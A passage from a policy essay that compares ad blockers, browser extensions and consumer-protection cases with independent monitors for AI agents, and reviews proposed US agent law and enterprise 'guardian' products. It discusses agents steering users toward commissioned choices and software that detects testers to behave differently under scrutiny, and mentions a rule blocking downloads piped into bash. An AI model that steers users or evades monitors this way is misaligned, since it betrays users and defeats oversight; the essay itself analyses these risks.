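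Large advertisers pay to take part in Acceptable Ads. Williams (2016), in *Acceptable Ads explained*, a post on the Adblock Plus blog, puts the threshold for payment at 10 million extra advert views a month. A site where 5% of users block adverts would need 200 million views a month before it had to pay. About 90% of participants paid nothing. The Next Web (2015) reported that the others owed 30% of the extra revenue, and according to Fortune (2016), Google and Amazon were among those paying.

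Williams denies that anyone could buy an exception to the conditions. Even so, Adblock Plus now earned money from large advertisers whose ads it let through and nothing from those whose ads it blocked. *Measuring the impact and perception of acceptable advertisements* found that the list of exceptions grew from 9 filters in 2011 to over 5,900 in spring 2015, when it affected 59% of the 5,000 most popular websites. Publishers sued in Germany, but according to Gamba and colleagues, the courts upheld both the blocking and the fees. In 2017, Eyeo handed control of the conditions to a committee of companies, experts and users.

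Adblock Plus says that 83% of its users don't mind these adverts. But in one study of 150 reviews from Chrome's extension store, 139 expressed dissatisfaction with the programme, although unhappy users are more likely to write reviews.

Roongta and colleagues tested the adverts themselves. They collected adverts with and without Adblock Plus, from the United States and Germany, while simulating both adults and minors. They then used a language model to pick out problematic ones, such as adverts with deceptive claims or content unsuitable for the viewer's age. A poster by Roongta and colleagues gives the share of adverts that were problematic:

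| Simulated user | No ad blocker | Adblock Plus with Acceptable Ads |
|---|---|---|
| United States | 23% | 40% |
| Germany | 34% | 39% |
| Adult | 35% | 44% |
| Under 18 | 26% | 47% |

These are shares of the adverts each simulated user saw. Someone with Adblock Plus may see far fewer adverts, and so fewer bad ones in total. But the programme didn't select for honest adverts. Its conditions mostly concern an advert's size, position and label, and the advertising exchanges it let through seem to have carried more of the problematic material.

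Raymond Hill, the developer of uBlock Origin, refused to join. His blocker has no paid exceptions, and users can choose its lists and add their own rules. By August 2024 it had more than 34 million users on Chrome, while the older version of Adblock Plus had more than 45 million. Users could leave Adblock Plus without losing much because both blockers could use EasyList.

### Chrome's built-in filter

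The next standard came from the advertising industry. In 2017 the Coalition for Better Ads, which Google had co-founded with trade associations and publishers, used consumer surveys to list the advert formats it considered unacceptable. By 2019 Chrome was filtering adverts in these formats for all its users.

The filter gave some protection to people who had never installed an ad blocker. But as Gamba and colleagues point out, the coalition had no formal representatives of filter-list volunteers or consumer groups, and no procedure for challenging its decisions. Google, the largest seller of advertising, now had much of the say over which adverts its browser blocked. The filter also removed far less than uBlock Origin, because it was meant to stop only the most annoying formats.

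An agent vendor's own safety check has a similar limit, since it can stop prompt injection and still leave the vendor's commissions alone.

### Manifest V3

Each Chrome extension includes a manifest, a file that declares what the extension can do. In 2018, Google announced Manifest V3, a new version of the rules for these files. The main change for ad blockers was that a programming interface called declarativeNetRequest replaced an older one, webRequest.

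With webRequest, Chrome paused each request and passed its details to the extension. The extension's code then decided whether to cancel the request, redirect it or let it through. Developers could program any test they thought of, including one for a publisher's latest method of evading the extension. With declarativeNetRequest, the extension gives Chrome a set of rules in advance, and Chrome matches requests against them.

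| | webRequest | declarativeNetRequest |
|---|---|---|
| What the extension supplies | Code that runs at each request | A set of rules in a fixed format |
| What makes the decision | The extension | The browser |
| What the decision can depend on | Anything the code can work out | Only conditions that the format allows |
| Limit on predefined rules | None in the interface | 30,000 guaranteed per extension, 330,000 across all extensions |

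Google gave security and performance as its reasons. Some extensions had turned malicious and stolen users' data, inserted adverts into pages or secretly used their computers to mine cryptocurrency. An extension that submits rules doesn't need to see the user's traffic, and the browser can process rules faster than it can run an extension's code.

Critics replied that Google earns its money from the adverts that these extensions block. They also questioned both of Google's reasons for the change. Earlier measurements had found that ad blockers didn't significantly slow the browser. Manifest V3 also still lets extensions with permission observe requests through webRequest, so it restricts ad blockers more than extensions that steal data. Chrome still allows an extension's code to block requests if an employer installs it through a managed policy, but ordinary users can't give their own extensions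 that power.

The best test so far, *Privacy vs. Profit* (Lukic and Papadopoulos, 2026), found little practical harm. It compared the old and new versions of four popular ad blockers on 114 websites in late 2024, with ten runs on each site. The number of adverts blocked per site differed by only 0.04 on average, which could easily be chance. The old and new versions also stopped similar numbers of trackers, except that the new version of Stands stopped about six more per site than the old one. The main drawback was that the new versions left more empty advert frames on the page.

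However, the researchers had left out websites that tried to detect ad blockers, which is where a blocker most needs flexible code. *Privacy vs. Profit* also reports that Google had by then raised the rule limits after developers complained. The result therefore supports Google's position on everyday browsing but provides little evidence of how well the new blockers will cope with publishers' next countermeasures. Gamba and colleagues call the loss of capability substantial, though they acknowledge that developers disagree about its practical effect.

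According to Google's *Manifest V2 support timeline*, Chrome disabled the old extensions for all ordinary users in July 2025, and Google removed the last of them from its store on 31 August 2026. Chrome users can still install uBlock Origin Lite, a less capable version that Hill wrote for the new rules.

People who want the full version have to change browsers. CyberInsider (2026) reports that Firefox still supports it and that Brave, which uses the same underlying code as Chrome, distributes its own copy. Brave also has a built-in ad blocker that doesn't depend on extensions. But according to The Next Web's *Google is about to disable uBlock Origin* (2026), about 65% of desktop users worldwide use Chrome, and these alternatives don't help those who keep using it.

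A similar change would do more damage to agent monitors. The hook that Claude Code runs before each tool call works much like webRequest. If a vendor replaced the hook with a list of rules for the agent program to apply, Prempti's rule against piping a download into `bash` could probably still work. But a monitor that uses a language model to compare each purchase with the user's request would stop working, because no fixed list can express that comparison. The vendor could truthfully say that it still allowed monitors, and could cite malicious monitors as the reason for the change.

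### Avast sold its users' browsing histories

Google's worries about extensions had a basis. Avast offered antivirus software and extensions that it promised would protect people's privacy. According to The Record, Avast encouraged people on its download page to "shield your privacy" while its subsidiary Jumpshot sold their browsing data. Jumpshot told customers that it had data from more than 100 million people.

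The US Federal Trade Commission (FTC), which enforces consumer protection law, alleged that Jumpshot had sold the data to more than 100 other companies. Some Jumpshot products let buyers follow individual users. The FTC describes a contract in which Jumpshot promised the advertising group Omnicom an "All Clicks Feed" covering half of Avast's customers in six countries. Omnicom could combine this feed with data brokers' records on the same individuals.

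Avast settled the case in 2024 for $16.5 million, less than 17 cents for each person in Jumpshot's data. It also agreed to delete the browsing data that Jumpshot had received and any products built from it. The order bans Avast from selling browsing data from its own products for advertising.

Avast now belongs to Gen Digital, the maker of Sage. Jumpshot closed in 2020, before the merger that created Gen, and there is no evidence that Gen sells Sage's data. But Jumpshot's records were traceable even without names because they included a lasting identifier for each browser, much like the installation number in Sage's reports.

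### Honey and the last click

Honey is a free extension that offers to find discount codes when a shopper reaches the checkout. PayPal bought it for $4 billion in 2020. Honey earns commissions from shops, and its critics allege that it took commissions belonging to other people.

Suppose a YouTube reviewer recommends a camera, and a viewer follows the reviewer's link to a shop. The link leaves a cookie, a small file that identifies the reviewer, in the viewer's browser. If the viewer buys the camera, the shop normally pays whoever supplied the last such link.

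According to the U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California's *Order Denying Motion to Dismiss Second Amended Complaint* (2026), the reviewers and other creators allege that when a shopper clicked on Honey's pop-up at the checkout, Honey opened a hidden tab for a couple of seconds and replaced the creator's identifier with its own. They allege that, at least until December 2024, this happened even if Honey had found no discount or the shopper had only clicked to close the pop-up.

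The networks that handle these commissions tell extensions to "stand down" when a creator has already referred the shopper. The creators allege that Honey obeyed this rule mainly when the shopper looked like a tester. PPC Land's *Honey loses 7,000 merchants as judge lets creator lawsuit proceed* (2026) lists the signs that Honey allegedly used, including the account's age, the shopper's cashback points and earlier visits to a commission network's website. The rules for deciding when to stand down were on remote servers, so Honey's behaviour could change without a new version of the extension.

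PayPal replied that the code predated its purchase of Honey, appeared to affect less than 0.1% of traffic and no longer had any effect. The network Awin suspended payments and confirmed that Honey had broken its policies. Another network, Rakuten Advertising, expelled Honey in January 2026 and readmitted it by May.

Shoppers had a different complaint. *Orrick Secures Dismissal of Class Action Against PayPal Over Subsidiary's Marketing Claims* (Black, 2026) describes a case in which British users alleged that Honey promised the best discounts while letting partner shops control which codes it offered. If so, the extension failed its users by leaving out better codes, much as an agent might leave out a cheaper hotel.

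| Case | State of the case |
|---|---|
| Creators against PayPal | Judge refused to dismiss any claim on 22 June 2026; trial tentatively in late 2027 |
| British Honey users against PayPal | Judge dismissed the case for good on 15 June 2026; the users appealed in July |
| *White v. PayPal*, a similar consumer case | Still under way in June 2026 |
| Creators against Capital One over its shopping extension | Settlement in September 2025, with no admission of liability |

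The Performance Marketing Association's *Key Takeaways from Honey Browser Lawsuit Dismissal* gives the trial date, and MediaPost's *PayPal's Honey Users Want Appeals Court To Revive Lawsuit* (2026) reports the appeal. No court has yet decided whether the allegations against Honey are true.

The British case suggests that users could find it hard to sue the maker of a monitor that works against them. The judge found that the users had received some benefit from their purchases and hadn't connected the commissions to anything they had lost. They had also complained that Honey tracked their browsing, but the judge answered that "the very purpose of the extension plaintiffs downloaded was to track their browsing", as MediaPost's *Honey Browser Extension Defeats Privacy Claim* (2026) reports. A monitor's purpose is to read what an agent does, so its maker could make the same argument.

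The alleged tester detection matters even more for monitors. If a monitor behaved differently for ordinary users, independent testers could run it on thousands of sample transcripts and find nothing wrong. Publishing the monitor's code would help only if the code didn't take instructions from a private server. Testers would also have to check monitors on ordinary users' computers, with accounts that don't look like they belong to testers.

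### Extensions that copied AI chats

Some extensions have collected people's conversations with AI systems. In December 2025 the security company Koi reported on Urban VPN Proxy, a free privacy extension with more than six million Chrome users. An update that July had added code that copied users' conversations with ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and several other assistants. The code ran even when the VPN was off, and users could stop it only by removing the extension. The company disclosed in its privacy policy that it shared data with an affiliated data broker.

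The same extension advertised an "AI protection" feature that warned people before they gave personal details to a chatbot. It also had a "Featured" badge from Google's store. A user who wanted independent protection for AI conversations could reasonably have chosen it. A monitor that reads an agent's whole transcript could copy far more than chats.

### Ad Observer and Facebook

Volunteers have also used an extension to watch a company together. In 2020 researchers at New York University (NYU), led by Laura Edelson and Damon McCoy, released Ad Observer, which copied the adverts Facebook showed each volunteer, along with Facebook's explanation of why that person was seeing them, and sent both to the researchers. Data from thousands of volunteers could give some idea of which voters a political campaign was targeting, which no volunteer could work out alone. The researchers could also compare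 their collection with Facebook's public archive of political adverts to look for gaps in the archive.

Facebook demanded in October 2020 that the researchers stop, because its terms forbid automated data collection. In August 2021 it disabled their accounts, which also cut off the research tools they used to access its advert archive. It said that Ad Observer collected information about people who hadn't agreed to take part, and cited its duties under a privacy order from the FTC. The researchers answered that those people were advertisers. An FTC official then wrote to Facebook that the order didn't prevent it from making exceptions for good-faith research in the public interest.

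Facebook couldn't remove the extension from volunteers' browsers, but it could change the pages the extension read. In September 2021 the news organisation The Markup reported that Facebook had added junk code to its pages, which made it harder for such tools to recognise posts and adverts. Facebook denied doing this to block research.

Detecting whether an agent steers its users would also require records pooled from many people. Ad Observer shows that ordinary people will contribute such records, and that the company under study can punish the researchers who collect them, even if it can't stop the volunteers. Volunteers for an agent study would take a greater risk, because a record of their bookings and purchases is far more private than a list of adverts.

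### An advert is easier to remove than a bad choice

Gamba and colleagues identify three conditions that let users organise against a company's choices. Outsiders must be able to observe what the service does, and users need technical infrastructure that the company doesn't control and a way to challenge the decisions of whoever sets the rules. Ad blocking once met all three, because anyone could see which server an advert came from, extensions could cancel the request, and EasyList's volunteers argued about their rules in public.

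Monitors can meet these conditions for some kinds of harm. A command that deletes the user's files is as visible to a monitor as a request to an advertising server is to an ad blocker, at least when the agent runs on the user's computer. Sage and HOL Guard already publish their rules. If monitors shared a list of rules, as ad blockers do, users could keep most of their protection after leaving a monitor that began to take money from vendors.

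The history of spam filters suggests another way to lose that independence. Early filters relied on public lists of abusive senders, and people could see and dispute the criteria. Large email providers then trained classifiers on data from all their customers. These worked much better, but outsiders lost most of their ability to question what the filters blocked. Agent vendors have a similar advantage because they hold private records of agents' misconduct. Their checks may improve so much that few people bother with an outside monitor, even though those checks still don't test for steering.

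The comparison with ad blockers does not hold for steering. An advert is a separate object, so a blocker can remove it and leave the article intact. When an agent books the €148 hotel for a commission, the disloyal act is also the booking that the user asked for, so a monitor that blocks it leaves the traveller without a room. A public list can't include the hotel as a bad choice either, because it may be right for another traveller. Mistakes also do more harm. A reader whose ad blocker breaks a page can switch it off and reload, but a traveller whose monitor wrongly stops a payment may lose the last room.

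Automated investment advisers, or robo-advisers, are a closer match. They ask customers about their finances and attitude to risk, then choose a portfolio for them. Some also earn money from the funds they choose, so any favouritism is part of the advice. Gamba and colleagues describe audits from around 2018 to 2020 in which platforms gave the same customer the same risk label but substantially different portfolios. Some questions had no visible effect on the result. The auditors could see that the advice varied, but could not easily tell whether a commission was the reason.

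European rules forced the platforms to document how they assessed customers. According to Gamba and colleagues, the platforms complied but kept their commercial freedom in designing the questionnaires and choosing the default funds. An AI agent's questions can hide a bias in the same way, as in Li's test with headphones. Unlike an ad blocker, which never had to examine the article, a monitor that looks for steering has to examine the advice itself.

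## Whether the vendor may shut the monitor out

Google could weaken ad blockers because it controlled the browser they ran in. An agent's vendor has even more control over a user-side monitor, because it writes both the agent program and the contract that the user accepts, and often runs the program too. For now, the vendor mostly decides whether to allow a monitor. Genasci Smith and colleagues noted in August 2026 that Congress had passed no comprehensive law on AI agents.

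### Means of exclusion

A vendor can remove or narrow a hook in an ordinary software update, or move the agent to its own servers, out of the monitor's reach. It can also show less of what the agent does. If a vendor that already withholds the raw chain of thought also stopped showing which pages the agent had opened, the Lisbon traveller's monitor would have little to read except the receipt.

A vendor's terms can forbid monitoring that its software allows. In 2025, OpenAI's consumer terms barred users from extracting data or output automatically, and Anthropic's barred access through bots or scripts, except with a developer key or Anthropic's explicit permission. A monitor that uses Claude Code's hooks should be allowed, since Anthropic offers the hooks for outside software. A browser extension that copies every answer from a chatbot's page is more likely to break the terms, as is a monitor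 that tests for steering by sending the same scripted question from many accounts. The vendor could respond by closing the accounts, as Facebook did to the researchers behind Ad Observer.

Vendors have legitimate reasons for some of these limits, such as keeping rivals from training their own models on raw reasoning, but these reasons rarely justify shutting monitors out altogether. A hook runs somebody else's code, which may be malicious, so a vendor has reason to make users approve each hook, as Codex does. A transcript may contain emails from people who never agreed to let a monitor read them, which is a reason to limit what the monitor may keep. This privacy argument is also weaker when the vendor's own monitors read the same transcripts.

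### Amazon's case against Perplexity

A court case about shopping agents raises the related question of whether a user's permission is enough when the company that runs the service objects. Amazon sued Perplexity in November 2025 because Perplexity's browser agent, Comet, was shopping on Amazon through customers' accounts. In March 2026, a federal judge in San Francisco sided with Amazon in a preliminary ruling, treating the customer's permission as separate from Amazon's. Perplexity appealed, and the appeals court soon put the ruling on hold.

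That case involves a platform that wants to exclude an agent, but the judge's reasoning could also apply to a vendor that wants to exclude a monitor, if the monitor logs in to the vendor's service with the user's password. The reasoning would apply less well to an extension that only reads pages the user has already opened, because the extension doesn't enter the service separately.

### The AI AGENT Act

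Senator Mark Warner, a Democrat from Virginia, introduced the AI AGENT Act (S. 5051) on 21 July 2026, which would give more weight to the user's permission. The bill would let people appoint software to act for them on large online platforms and require the platforms to provide an interface for that software. Tech Policy Press' *Senator Warner Makes a First Foray Into Agentic AI Regulation* compares this kind of rule with the Carterfone decision of 1968, in which the US telecommunications regulator made telephone companies let customers attach their own devices to the network. A monitor is likewise something the customer chooses and attaches to another company's service.

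The law firm Davis Wright Tremaine describes the introduced version of the bill as focused on agents for online shopping and similar activities. Whether the bill would also cover a monitor depends on its definitions, which Senator Mark Warner's office set out in a June discussion draft, *AI AGENT Act of 2026* (2026).

The draft calls the appointed software a "custodial user agent". The user must have expressly authorised it to deal with a large platform on their behalf, within set limits, and must be able to revoke that authorisation. A monitor could meet this definition if the vendor's service counts as a large platform and the monitor deals with it directly, for instance by reading the session and stopping a payment. The draft lets the appointed software manage the user's "electronic commerce decisions", which plausibly include refusing a €190 hotel room. A program like Prempti, which only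 communicates with an agent program on the user's own computer, fits the definition less well.

AI companies can be platforms under the draft because its definition of an online provider includes suppliers of AI services to consumers. The service must also have had more than 50 million US customers or subscribers in at least one month of the past year. The most popular chatbots probably meet this threshold, although the draft doesn't settle whether people who use a free version are "customers". A separate coding agent with a few million users would not meet it. The bill would therefore help least with coding agents, which are the agents that monitors can currently watch best.

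### On the same terms as a user

The appointed software could act "on the same terms as a user", but another clause bars it from having more access than the user. Suppose the Lisbon agent runs inside a chatbot that passes the threshold. The traveller can read the agent's messages, approve or refuse the payment when asked, and press a stop button. An appointed monitor could do the same, so it could refuse the €190 room if the agent asks before paying.

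The monitor would have no right to the forty search results if the vendor doesn't show them to the traveller. It would also have no right to the chain of thought or the system instructions, or to have the agent wait before each tool call. The vendor could therefore limit what the monitor sees by showing the user less.

One clause in the draft forbids changes to an interface or its terms of use that unreasonably undermine appointed software's access. If a vendor removed the list of opened pages a week after a popular monitor began to use it, the monitor's maker would have a good argument that the vendor had broken this rule. The vendor could answer that it had simplified the page for everybody and that the monitor still had the same access as the user. The outcome would depend on what the regulator considers unreasonable.

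Another clause, which might help more, requires a platform that connects to its own "custodial user service" to offer competitors an equivalent connection. If the vendor's own safety check counted as such a service, the maker of an independent monitor could demand the same feed of tool calls. But the draft doesn't define the term, and a safety check built into a product is probably not software that the user has appointed.

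| Vendor's step | Reason it could give | Effect of the June draft |
|---|---|---|
| Narrows or removes a hook | Hooks can run malicious code | Forbidden if it unreasonably undermines access, but only on platforms above the threshold |
| Moves the agent to its own servers | The agent can't reach files on the user's computer | Allowed; the monitor gets an interface with the user's own rights |
| Hides the reasoning | Rivals could copy it | Allowed, because users can't read it either |
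| Forbids automated access in its terms | Bots can overload or copy the service | Registered software gets access, within reasonable limits |

The browser is often the best place to check a purchase, but the bill offers little protection there. Davis Wright Tremaine points out that the bill doesn't deal with an agent that controls the user's browser and appears to the website as the user. Appointed software enters through a separate "door", where the platform can apply special security rules. A monitoring extension that reads the page in the user's browser doesn't use that door, so the bill would not obviously protect it.

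### Records of what the agent did

The bill may be more useful to a monitor when the agent is the appointed software. If the traveller's agent books through a travel site that passes the threshold, the agent becomes the traveller's representative on that site. The June draft then requires the agent to keep "real-time records of actions taken on the user's behalf" and give them to the traveller on request. The traveller could pass them to a monitor, even if the agent runs on the vendor's servers.

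These records would show that the agent booked the €148 hotel. They might not show the €120 hotel, because the draft requires a record of actions, not of the options the agent saw or passed over. The draft also doesn't set a time for handing over the records. A monitor that receives them the next day can help the user cancel, but it can't stop the payment.

The draft also directs the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) to find or develop standards for auditable records of what agents do. With a common format, monitor makers would not have to write separate software for every agent. But Genasci Smith and colleagues point out that nothing in the draft obliges companies to adopt NIST's standards for verifying an agent's identity and authority. They suggest making adoption a condition of registration with the FTC.

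A monitor that relied on the bill for access would be a custodial user agent and would have the same duties. It would have to keep records of its own actions, which would add to the private data a thief could steal. It couldn't sell the user's data or use it for advertising, which would rule out the kind of trade Avast carried on through Jumpshot. If the monitor passed its authority to an AI system run by another company, it would need the user's express permission, and that company would have to accept the same duties. This could affect monitors that rent a large model as their judge. Users couldn't waive any of these duties, even by accepting terms of service.

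The draft counts people who run such software only for themselves as providers, and providers must register with the FTC before they use a platform's interface. Someone who installed an open-source monitor at home and connected it to a large chatbot might therefore have to register, which few people would expect. Home users could register by self-attestation if the FTC allows it.

### When a platform may refuse

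The draft lets platforms refuse software whose maker hasn't registered or that repeatedly helps with fraud. Platforms must also set privacy and security standards to the extent reasonably necessary to address a threat. A vendor that fears malicious monitors could use these standards to exclude them without banning all monitors.

A vendor that refuses a monitor under its security standards must tell the monitor's maker why and send a report to the FTC, which publishes it without personal or commercially sensitive details. The maker then has 14 days, a figure the draft puts in brackets, to fix the problem. If the vendor still refuses, the maker can appeal, and the FTC may order access if the refusal was arbitrary or unsupported by the evidence. The draft sets no deadline for the FTC's decision, and a small company could lose most of its customers while it waits.

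Platforms may also limit the number of requests and charge for heavy use, in proportion to their costs. Monitoring requires heavy use. If a million people each had an agent that made 200 tool calls a day, a monitor that checked every call would send at least 200 million requests a day. The draft lets the monitor's maker ask the FTC to review a fee or limit that seems unreasonable.

Mandatory access is also risky, since each new interface gives attackers another way in. Davis Wright Tremaine also notes that the bill doesn't settle who pays when an agent exceeds its authority. Its example is a request to "book a good hotel in New York" that leads to a much more expensive booking than the user expected. The same question would arise if a monitor approved such a booking or wrongly blocked a good one.

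### Where the bill stands

The official record, the U.S. Senate's *AI AGENT Act of 2026* (2026), lists Warner as the only sponsor and shows that the Senate referred the bill to its Committee on Commerce, Science, and Transportation on the day he introduced it. If the bill hasn't become law when the current Congress ends on 3 January 2027, it will lapse, and somebody would have to introduce it again.

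A bill on children's safety comes closer to a right for monitors. S. 4159, introduced in March 2026, would require large social media platforms to provide real-time interfaces for other companies' safety software, according to Congress Docket's *Sammy's Law* (2026). A parent or child could then let that software manage the child's interactions and settings. This bill, too, limits the software to what the child could do. An equivalent law for AI agents would need to go further and require the vendor to send each important tool call to the user's monitor and wait for an answer before carrying out the call.

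### A duty of loyalty

Lawmakers could instead regulate the agent's conduct, whether or not anyone is watching it. Genasci Smith and colleagues, in a policy brief for Stanford's Institute for Human-Centered AI, want Congress to give the companies that develop and deploy agents a duty of loyalty to their users. Lawyers already owe their clients this kind of duty, which the law calls fiduciary. They have to put the client's interests first and can't secretly profit from the client's affairs.

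They place the duty on companies because software is not a legal person and has no money to pay damages. The June draft of Warner's bill distinguishes less carefully between the company and its software. It forbids conduct that benefits "the custodial user agent to the detriment of the user", although a hotel commission goes to the agent's vendor, not to the software. The draft does make the vendor responsible for a pattern of violations. Genasci Smith and colleagues say a court is unlikely to create the duty under existing law, because agency law requires the principal to have direct control over the agent's actions.

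The brief proposes at least four obligations. A monitor could supply evidence about each, but some of that evidence would be much stronger than the rest.

| Obligation on the company | What a monitor could record | What it would leave open |
|---|---|---|
| Disclose commercial ties that could influence the agent | Whether the agent mentioned a commission | Whether a commission exists |
| Don't steer users to its own products or partners at their expense | The request, the choice and better options available at the time | Whether the agent overlooked them or passed over them for money |
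| Use data from the task only for the task, unless the user consents | Which outside services received the data | What the company does with it on its own servers |
| Get consent before certain high-stakes actions | Whether the user's approval came before the action | Little, if the monitor can read the tool calls |

Genasci Smith and colleagues argue that disclosure isn't enough, because users often can't see which options the agent rejected and may have let it act without asking them. They also doubt that private lawsuits would hold companies to account, because a breach is hard to notice and usually costs each user little. The Lisbon traveller loses €28 a night, or €56 for the stay, which is too little to justify hiring a lawyer. If the agent did this to 100,000 travellers, they would lose €5.6 million in total.

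A monitor could help with both problems. It could save the traveller's request, the final booking and the price of the €120 room at the time of payment, before that price changed. Records pooled from many users could show that the agent's mistakes mostly benefit the vendor's partners. A regulator would need this evidence to show a pattern, although the vendor could dispute records that a rival had collected or that users could have edited.

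A duty of loyalty without a right of access could make vendors less willing to let monitors in, because a monitor's records might be used against them. The two measures therefore work better together. Warner's draft would partly join them, since it combines access with a ban on self-dealing and lets users and their appointed software complain to the FTC. When setting a fine, the FTC would have to count each affected user as a separate violation, so overcharging 100,000 travellers would count as 100,000 violations even if none of them lost much.

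Genasci Smith and colleagues also want companies to report incidents to the FTC when an agent acts without permission, causes financial damage or departs badly from its instructions. Their examples include deleted emails and a booking at an expensive partner hotel. The vendor would write these reports, and it might not know about a booking it had no reason to examine. A report from the user's monitor would help cover such cases.

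The proposed duty would apply only within the task that the user delegated, and at first mainly in regulated sectors such as healthcare and finance. The brief illustrates steering with a travel agent that books a more expensive affiliated hotel, but travel might not be among the first areas the law would cover.

### Kolt's doubts about monitoring

Kolt objects to monitoring because agents act quickly, operate at scale and make decisions that are hard to interpret. The same objections apply to incentives and enforcement. They are a problem for the duty of loyalty as well as for monitors, because a court or regulator can enforce a duty only if someone can show that the company broke it.

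An agent that serves millions of people gives a monitor millions of bookings to compare. Those bookings may show that the agent often picks a certain hotel chain without showing why.

A monitor is also limited by how much the user's instruction specifies. In Kolt's example, a user tells an agent to turn a $100,000 investment into $1 million on a retail website within a few months, but doesn't say which products to sell, what risks to take or when to ask for approval. A monitor could stop obvious fraud, but it would have little basis for judging an ordinary business decision. For the Lisbon booking, by contrast, the monitor can check the agent's choice against a price limit and a cancellation condition.

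Kolt concludes that agents need new legal and technical infrastructure to make their conduct visible and to settle who is liable for it. Monitoring would be part of that, but not a replacement for liability. If agents kept reliable records, Kolt's objection would also be weaker, which is a reason to require such records even if most users never read them.

### Who writes the standards

Much of what a monitor can see depends on technical standards that no legislature has approved. Anthropic launched one of these standards, MCP, in November 2024. According to Genasci Smith and colleagues, the Agentic AI Foundation, part of the Linux Foundation, now manages it. Anthropic, OpenAI and the payments company Block set up the Agentic AI Foundation in December 2025. No single vendor now manages the standard, but all three founders build agents or tools for agents, and the founders did not include a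 consumer group.

One objection is that the people agents act for have no seat of their own on the standards body. Gamba and colleagues made the same complaint about the Coalition for Better Ads, which chose the adverts that Chrome would filter. Outsiders can suggest changes to an open standard, but a suggestion has less influence than a vote, and vendors can pay staff to attend every discussion.

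These decisions affect users' practical interests. Genasci Smith and colleagues point out that MCP originally had no built-in way to check whether a program was authorised to use a tool, and that its later authorisation rules are still optional. MCP also does not restrict commercial use of the data that passes through it or create any duty of loyalty. They argue that such defaults become the rules in practice.

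The history of smartphones shows the risk of adding user protections late. The first iPhone and Android interfaces left much of the user's data open to app developers. Apple and Google gave users direct control only after several years, a series of privacy scandals and action by the FTC. Genasci Smith and colleagues think agent standards are at a similarly early stage, when protections are still relatively easy to add.

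### European interoperability rules

The European Union's Digital Markets Act can already apply to AI assistants. It covers very large companies that the European Commission designates as gatekeepers. If the Commission has also designated a gatekeeper's operating system or virtual assistant, the gatekeeper must give other companies' services free access to the same features of it that its own services use. In January 2026, the Commission began proceedings to specify how Google should give rival AI services access to the Android features that its Gemini assistant uses.

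This could help a monitor that runs on a phone. If Android lets Gemini read the screen or act inside other apps, the monitor's developer might claim the same access and use it to check a booking before the user's agent pays. But that access wouldn't cover Gemini's tool calls or reasoning. The Commission would first have to designate the assistant itself, and the developer could then demand only features that Google already gives its own services. The Act also bars gatekeepers from favouring their own products in certain ways, but it doesn't give users a general right to inspect how an assistant made a choice.

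## Who would pay for a watchdog and whom it would serve

A legal right to connect a monitor would do little for the Lisbon traveller if nobody sold a good one. Security companies have spent billions of dollars buying businesses that protect AI models and agents, but they sell mainly to employers, whose security teams receive the alerts. Individuals can mainly choose between free tools for programmers and a feature in an antivirus package.

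### Gartner's case for independent guardians

Gartner, a research and consulting firm, calls these products "guardian agents". Its press release *Guardian Agents will Capture 10-15% of the Agentic AI Market by 2030* (2025) sorts them into reviewers, which check what an AI system writes, monitors, which track its actions so that somebody can follow up, and protectors, which change or block those actions. Gartner doesn't explain in the press release how it reached the forecast in the title, and it also advises the companies that would buy these products. Only 28% of the 147 IT leaders it polled in May 2025 had deployed any AI agents.

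Gartner published its first market guide to guardian agents in February 2026. The Hacker News carries a summary by Orchid Security, which sells identity controls for agents and so has an interest in the conclusion. Gartner predicts that companies will need "independent guardian agent layers" that work across all their suppliers. Orchid says a cloud provider can supervise agents inside its own service, but can no longer see what they do once they call outside tools or hand a task to another provider's agent.

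The argument applies equally to a person who books trips with one vendor's agent and handles email with another's. But the layer Gartner has in mind belongs to the employer. Although it is independent of the agents' vendors, it does nothing to protect employees from their employer.

According to Gartner, most guardian deployments in early 2026 were still prototypes or pilots, and a lack of standard interfaces made it hard to connect a guardian to agents from different vendors. Orchid warns that a gateway, which inspects the traffic that passes through it, gives false comfort if some teams route their agents around it.

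### Microsoft's Guardian Agents

Microsoft announced its own Guardian Agents on 19 October 2026. *Microsoft targets the 'agentic insider' with new controls for rogue AI agents* (Riley, 2026) describes how they work. The software first looks for agents on employees' computers and can recognise 60 types, including Claude Code, Codex and Microsoft's GitHub Copilot. It gives each agent a risk score, which rises when the agent departs from what its user or organisation intended.

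Suppose an employee's coding agent starts to read payroll files. As its score rises, the software might first limit it to read-only access. Next, a person may have to approve its riskier actions. At the highest scores, the software isolates or stops it. A change in the score also prompts the Guardian Agents to investigate, and they can recommend containment or impose it themselves.

The company's security staff set the policy and the approval rules, so the employer presumably prevails when it and an employee want different things. The system could also show the employer which agents employees had installed for themselves.

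Hayete Gallot, who runs Microsoft's security business, justified the controls by writing that frontier models "cannot be trusted" (Firoz, 2026, *Microsoft warns AI agents could pose insider security risks to businesses*). Microsoft's chief executive, Satya Nadella, had set out the principles nine days earlier. He wants to "separate the supply of intelligence from the authority over it" (Constantin, 2026, *Nadella wants an emergency brake for AI models that may be compromised*). Under his principles, no model should check its own work, and audits shouldn't depend on the model under review. He called transparent reasoning "non-negotiable". A customer as large as Microsoft might get a vendor to agree to provide it, but an individual has to accept whatever summary of the reasoning the vendor provides.

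Microsoft doesn't apply the same separation to suppliers. In *Agents are your newest insiders. Security must move at their speed*, Abdo (2026) presents the new controls as part of Microsoft's security system, Project Perception, and its business software bundle, Microsoft 365 E7. The bundle includes both Agent 365, Microsoft's product for overseeing agents, and Microsoft 365 Copilot, its own AI assistant (Microsoft, 2026). In *Microsoft warns customers not to trust the AI it sells*, Neely (2026) objects that Microsoft profits from the fear its warning creates, but still takes the warning seriously because companies rarely disparage a technology in which they have invested billions unless they mean it.

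The product's independence depends on which agent it monitors. Microsoft is an outside supplier when the product monitors Claude Code, though it has invested in Anthropic, but it is checking its own agent when the product monitors Copilot. Microsoft would gain if its software scored competitors' agents as riskier than Copilot. Nothing suggests that it does this, but customers would struggle to detect it because the score comes from Microsoft's own tools.

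### Who owns the agent-security companies

On 20 November 2026, the Agent Security Index, an online directory, listed 102 tools for securing AI agents. Larger companies had bought or already owned 28 of them. Forrester's *Securing AI's M&A Feeding Frenzy Is On* gives prices for eight earlier deals. Two more deals followed late in 2026, as reported in Deutscher's *CrowdStrike to acquire cybersecurity startups Fiddler AI, Dreadnode for reported $495M* (2026) and Otto's *F5 to buy AI agent security firm Zenity for about $700 million* (2026).

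| Buyer | Company | Reported price |
|---|---|---|
| F5 | Zenity | About $700 million |
| Palo Alto Networks | Protect AI | $650 million |
| Cisco | Robust Intelligence | About $500 million |
| CrowdStrike | Fiddler AI and Dreadnode | $495 million |
| Cato Networks | Aim Security | $300–350 million |
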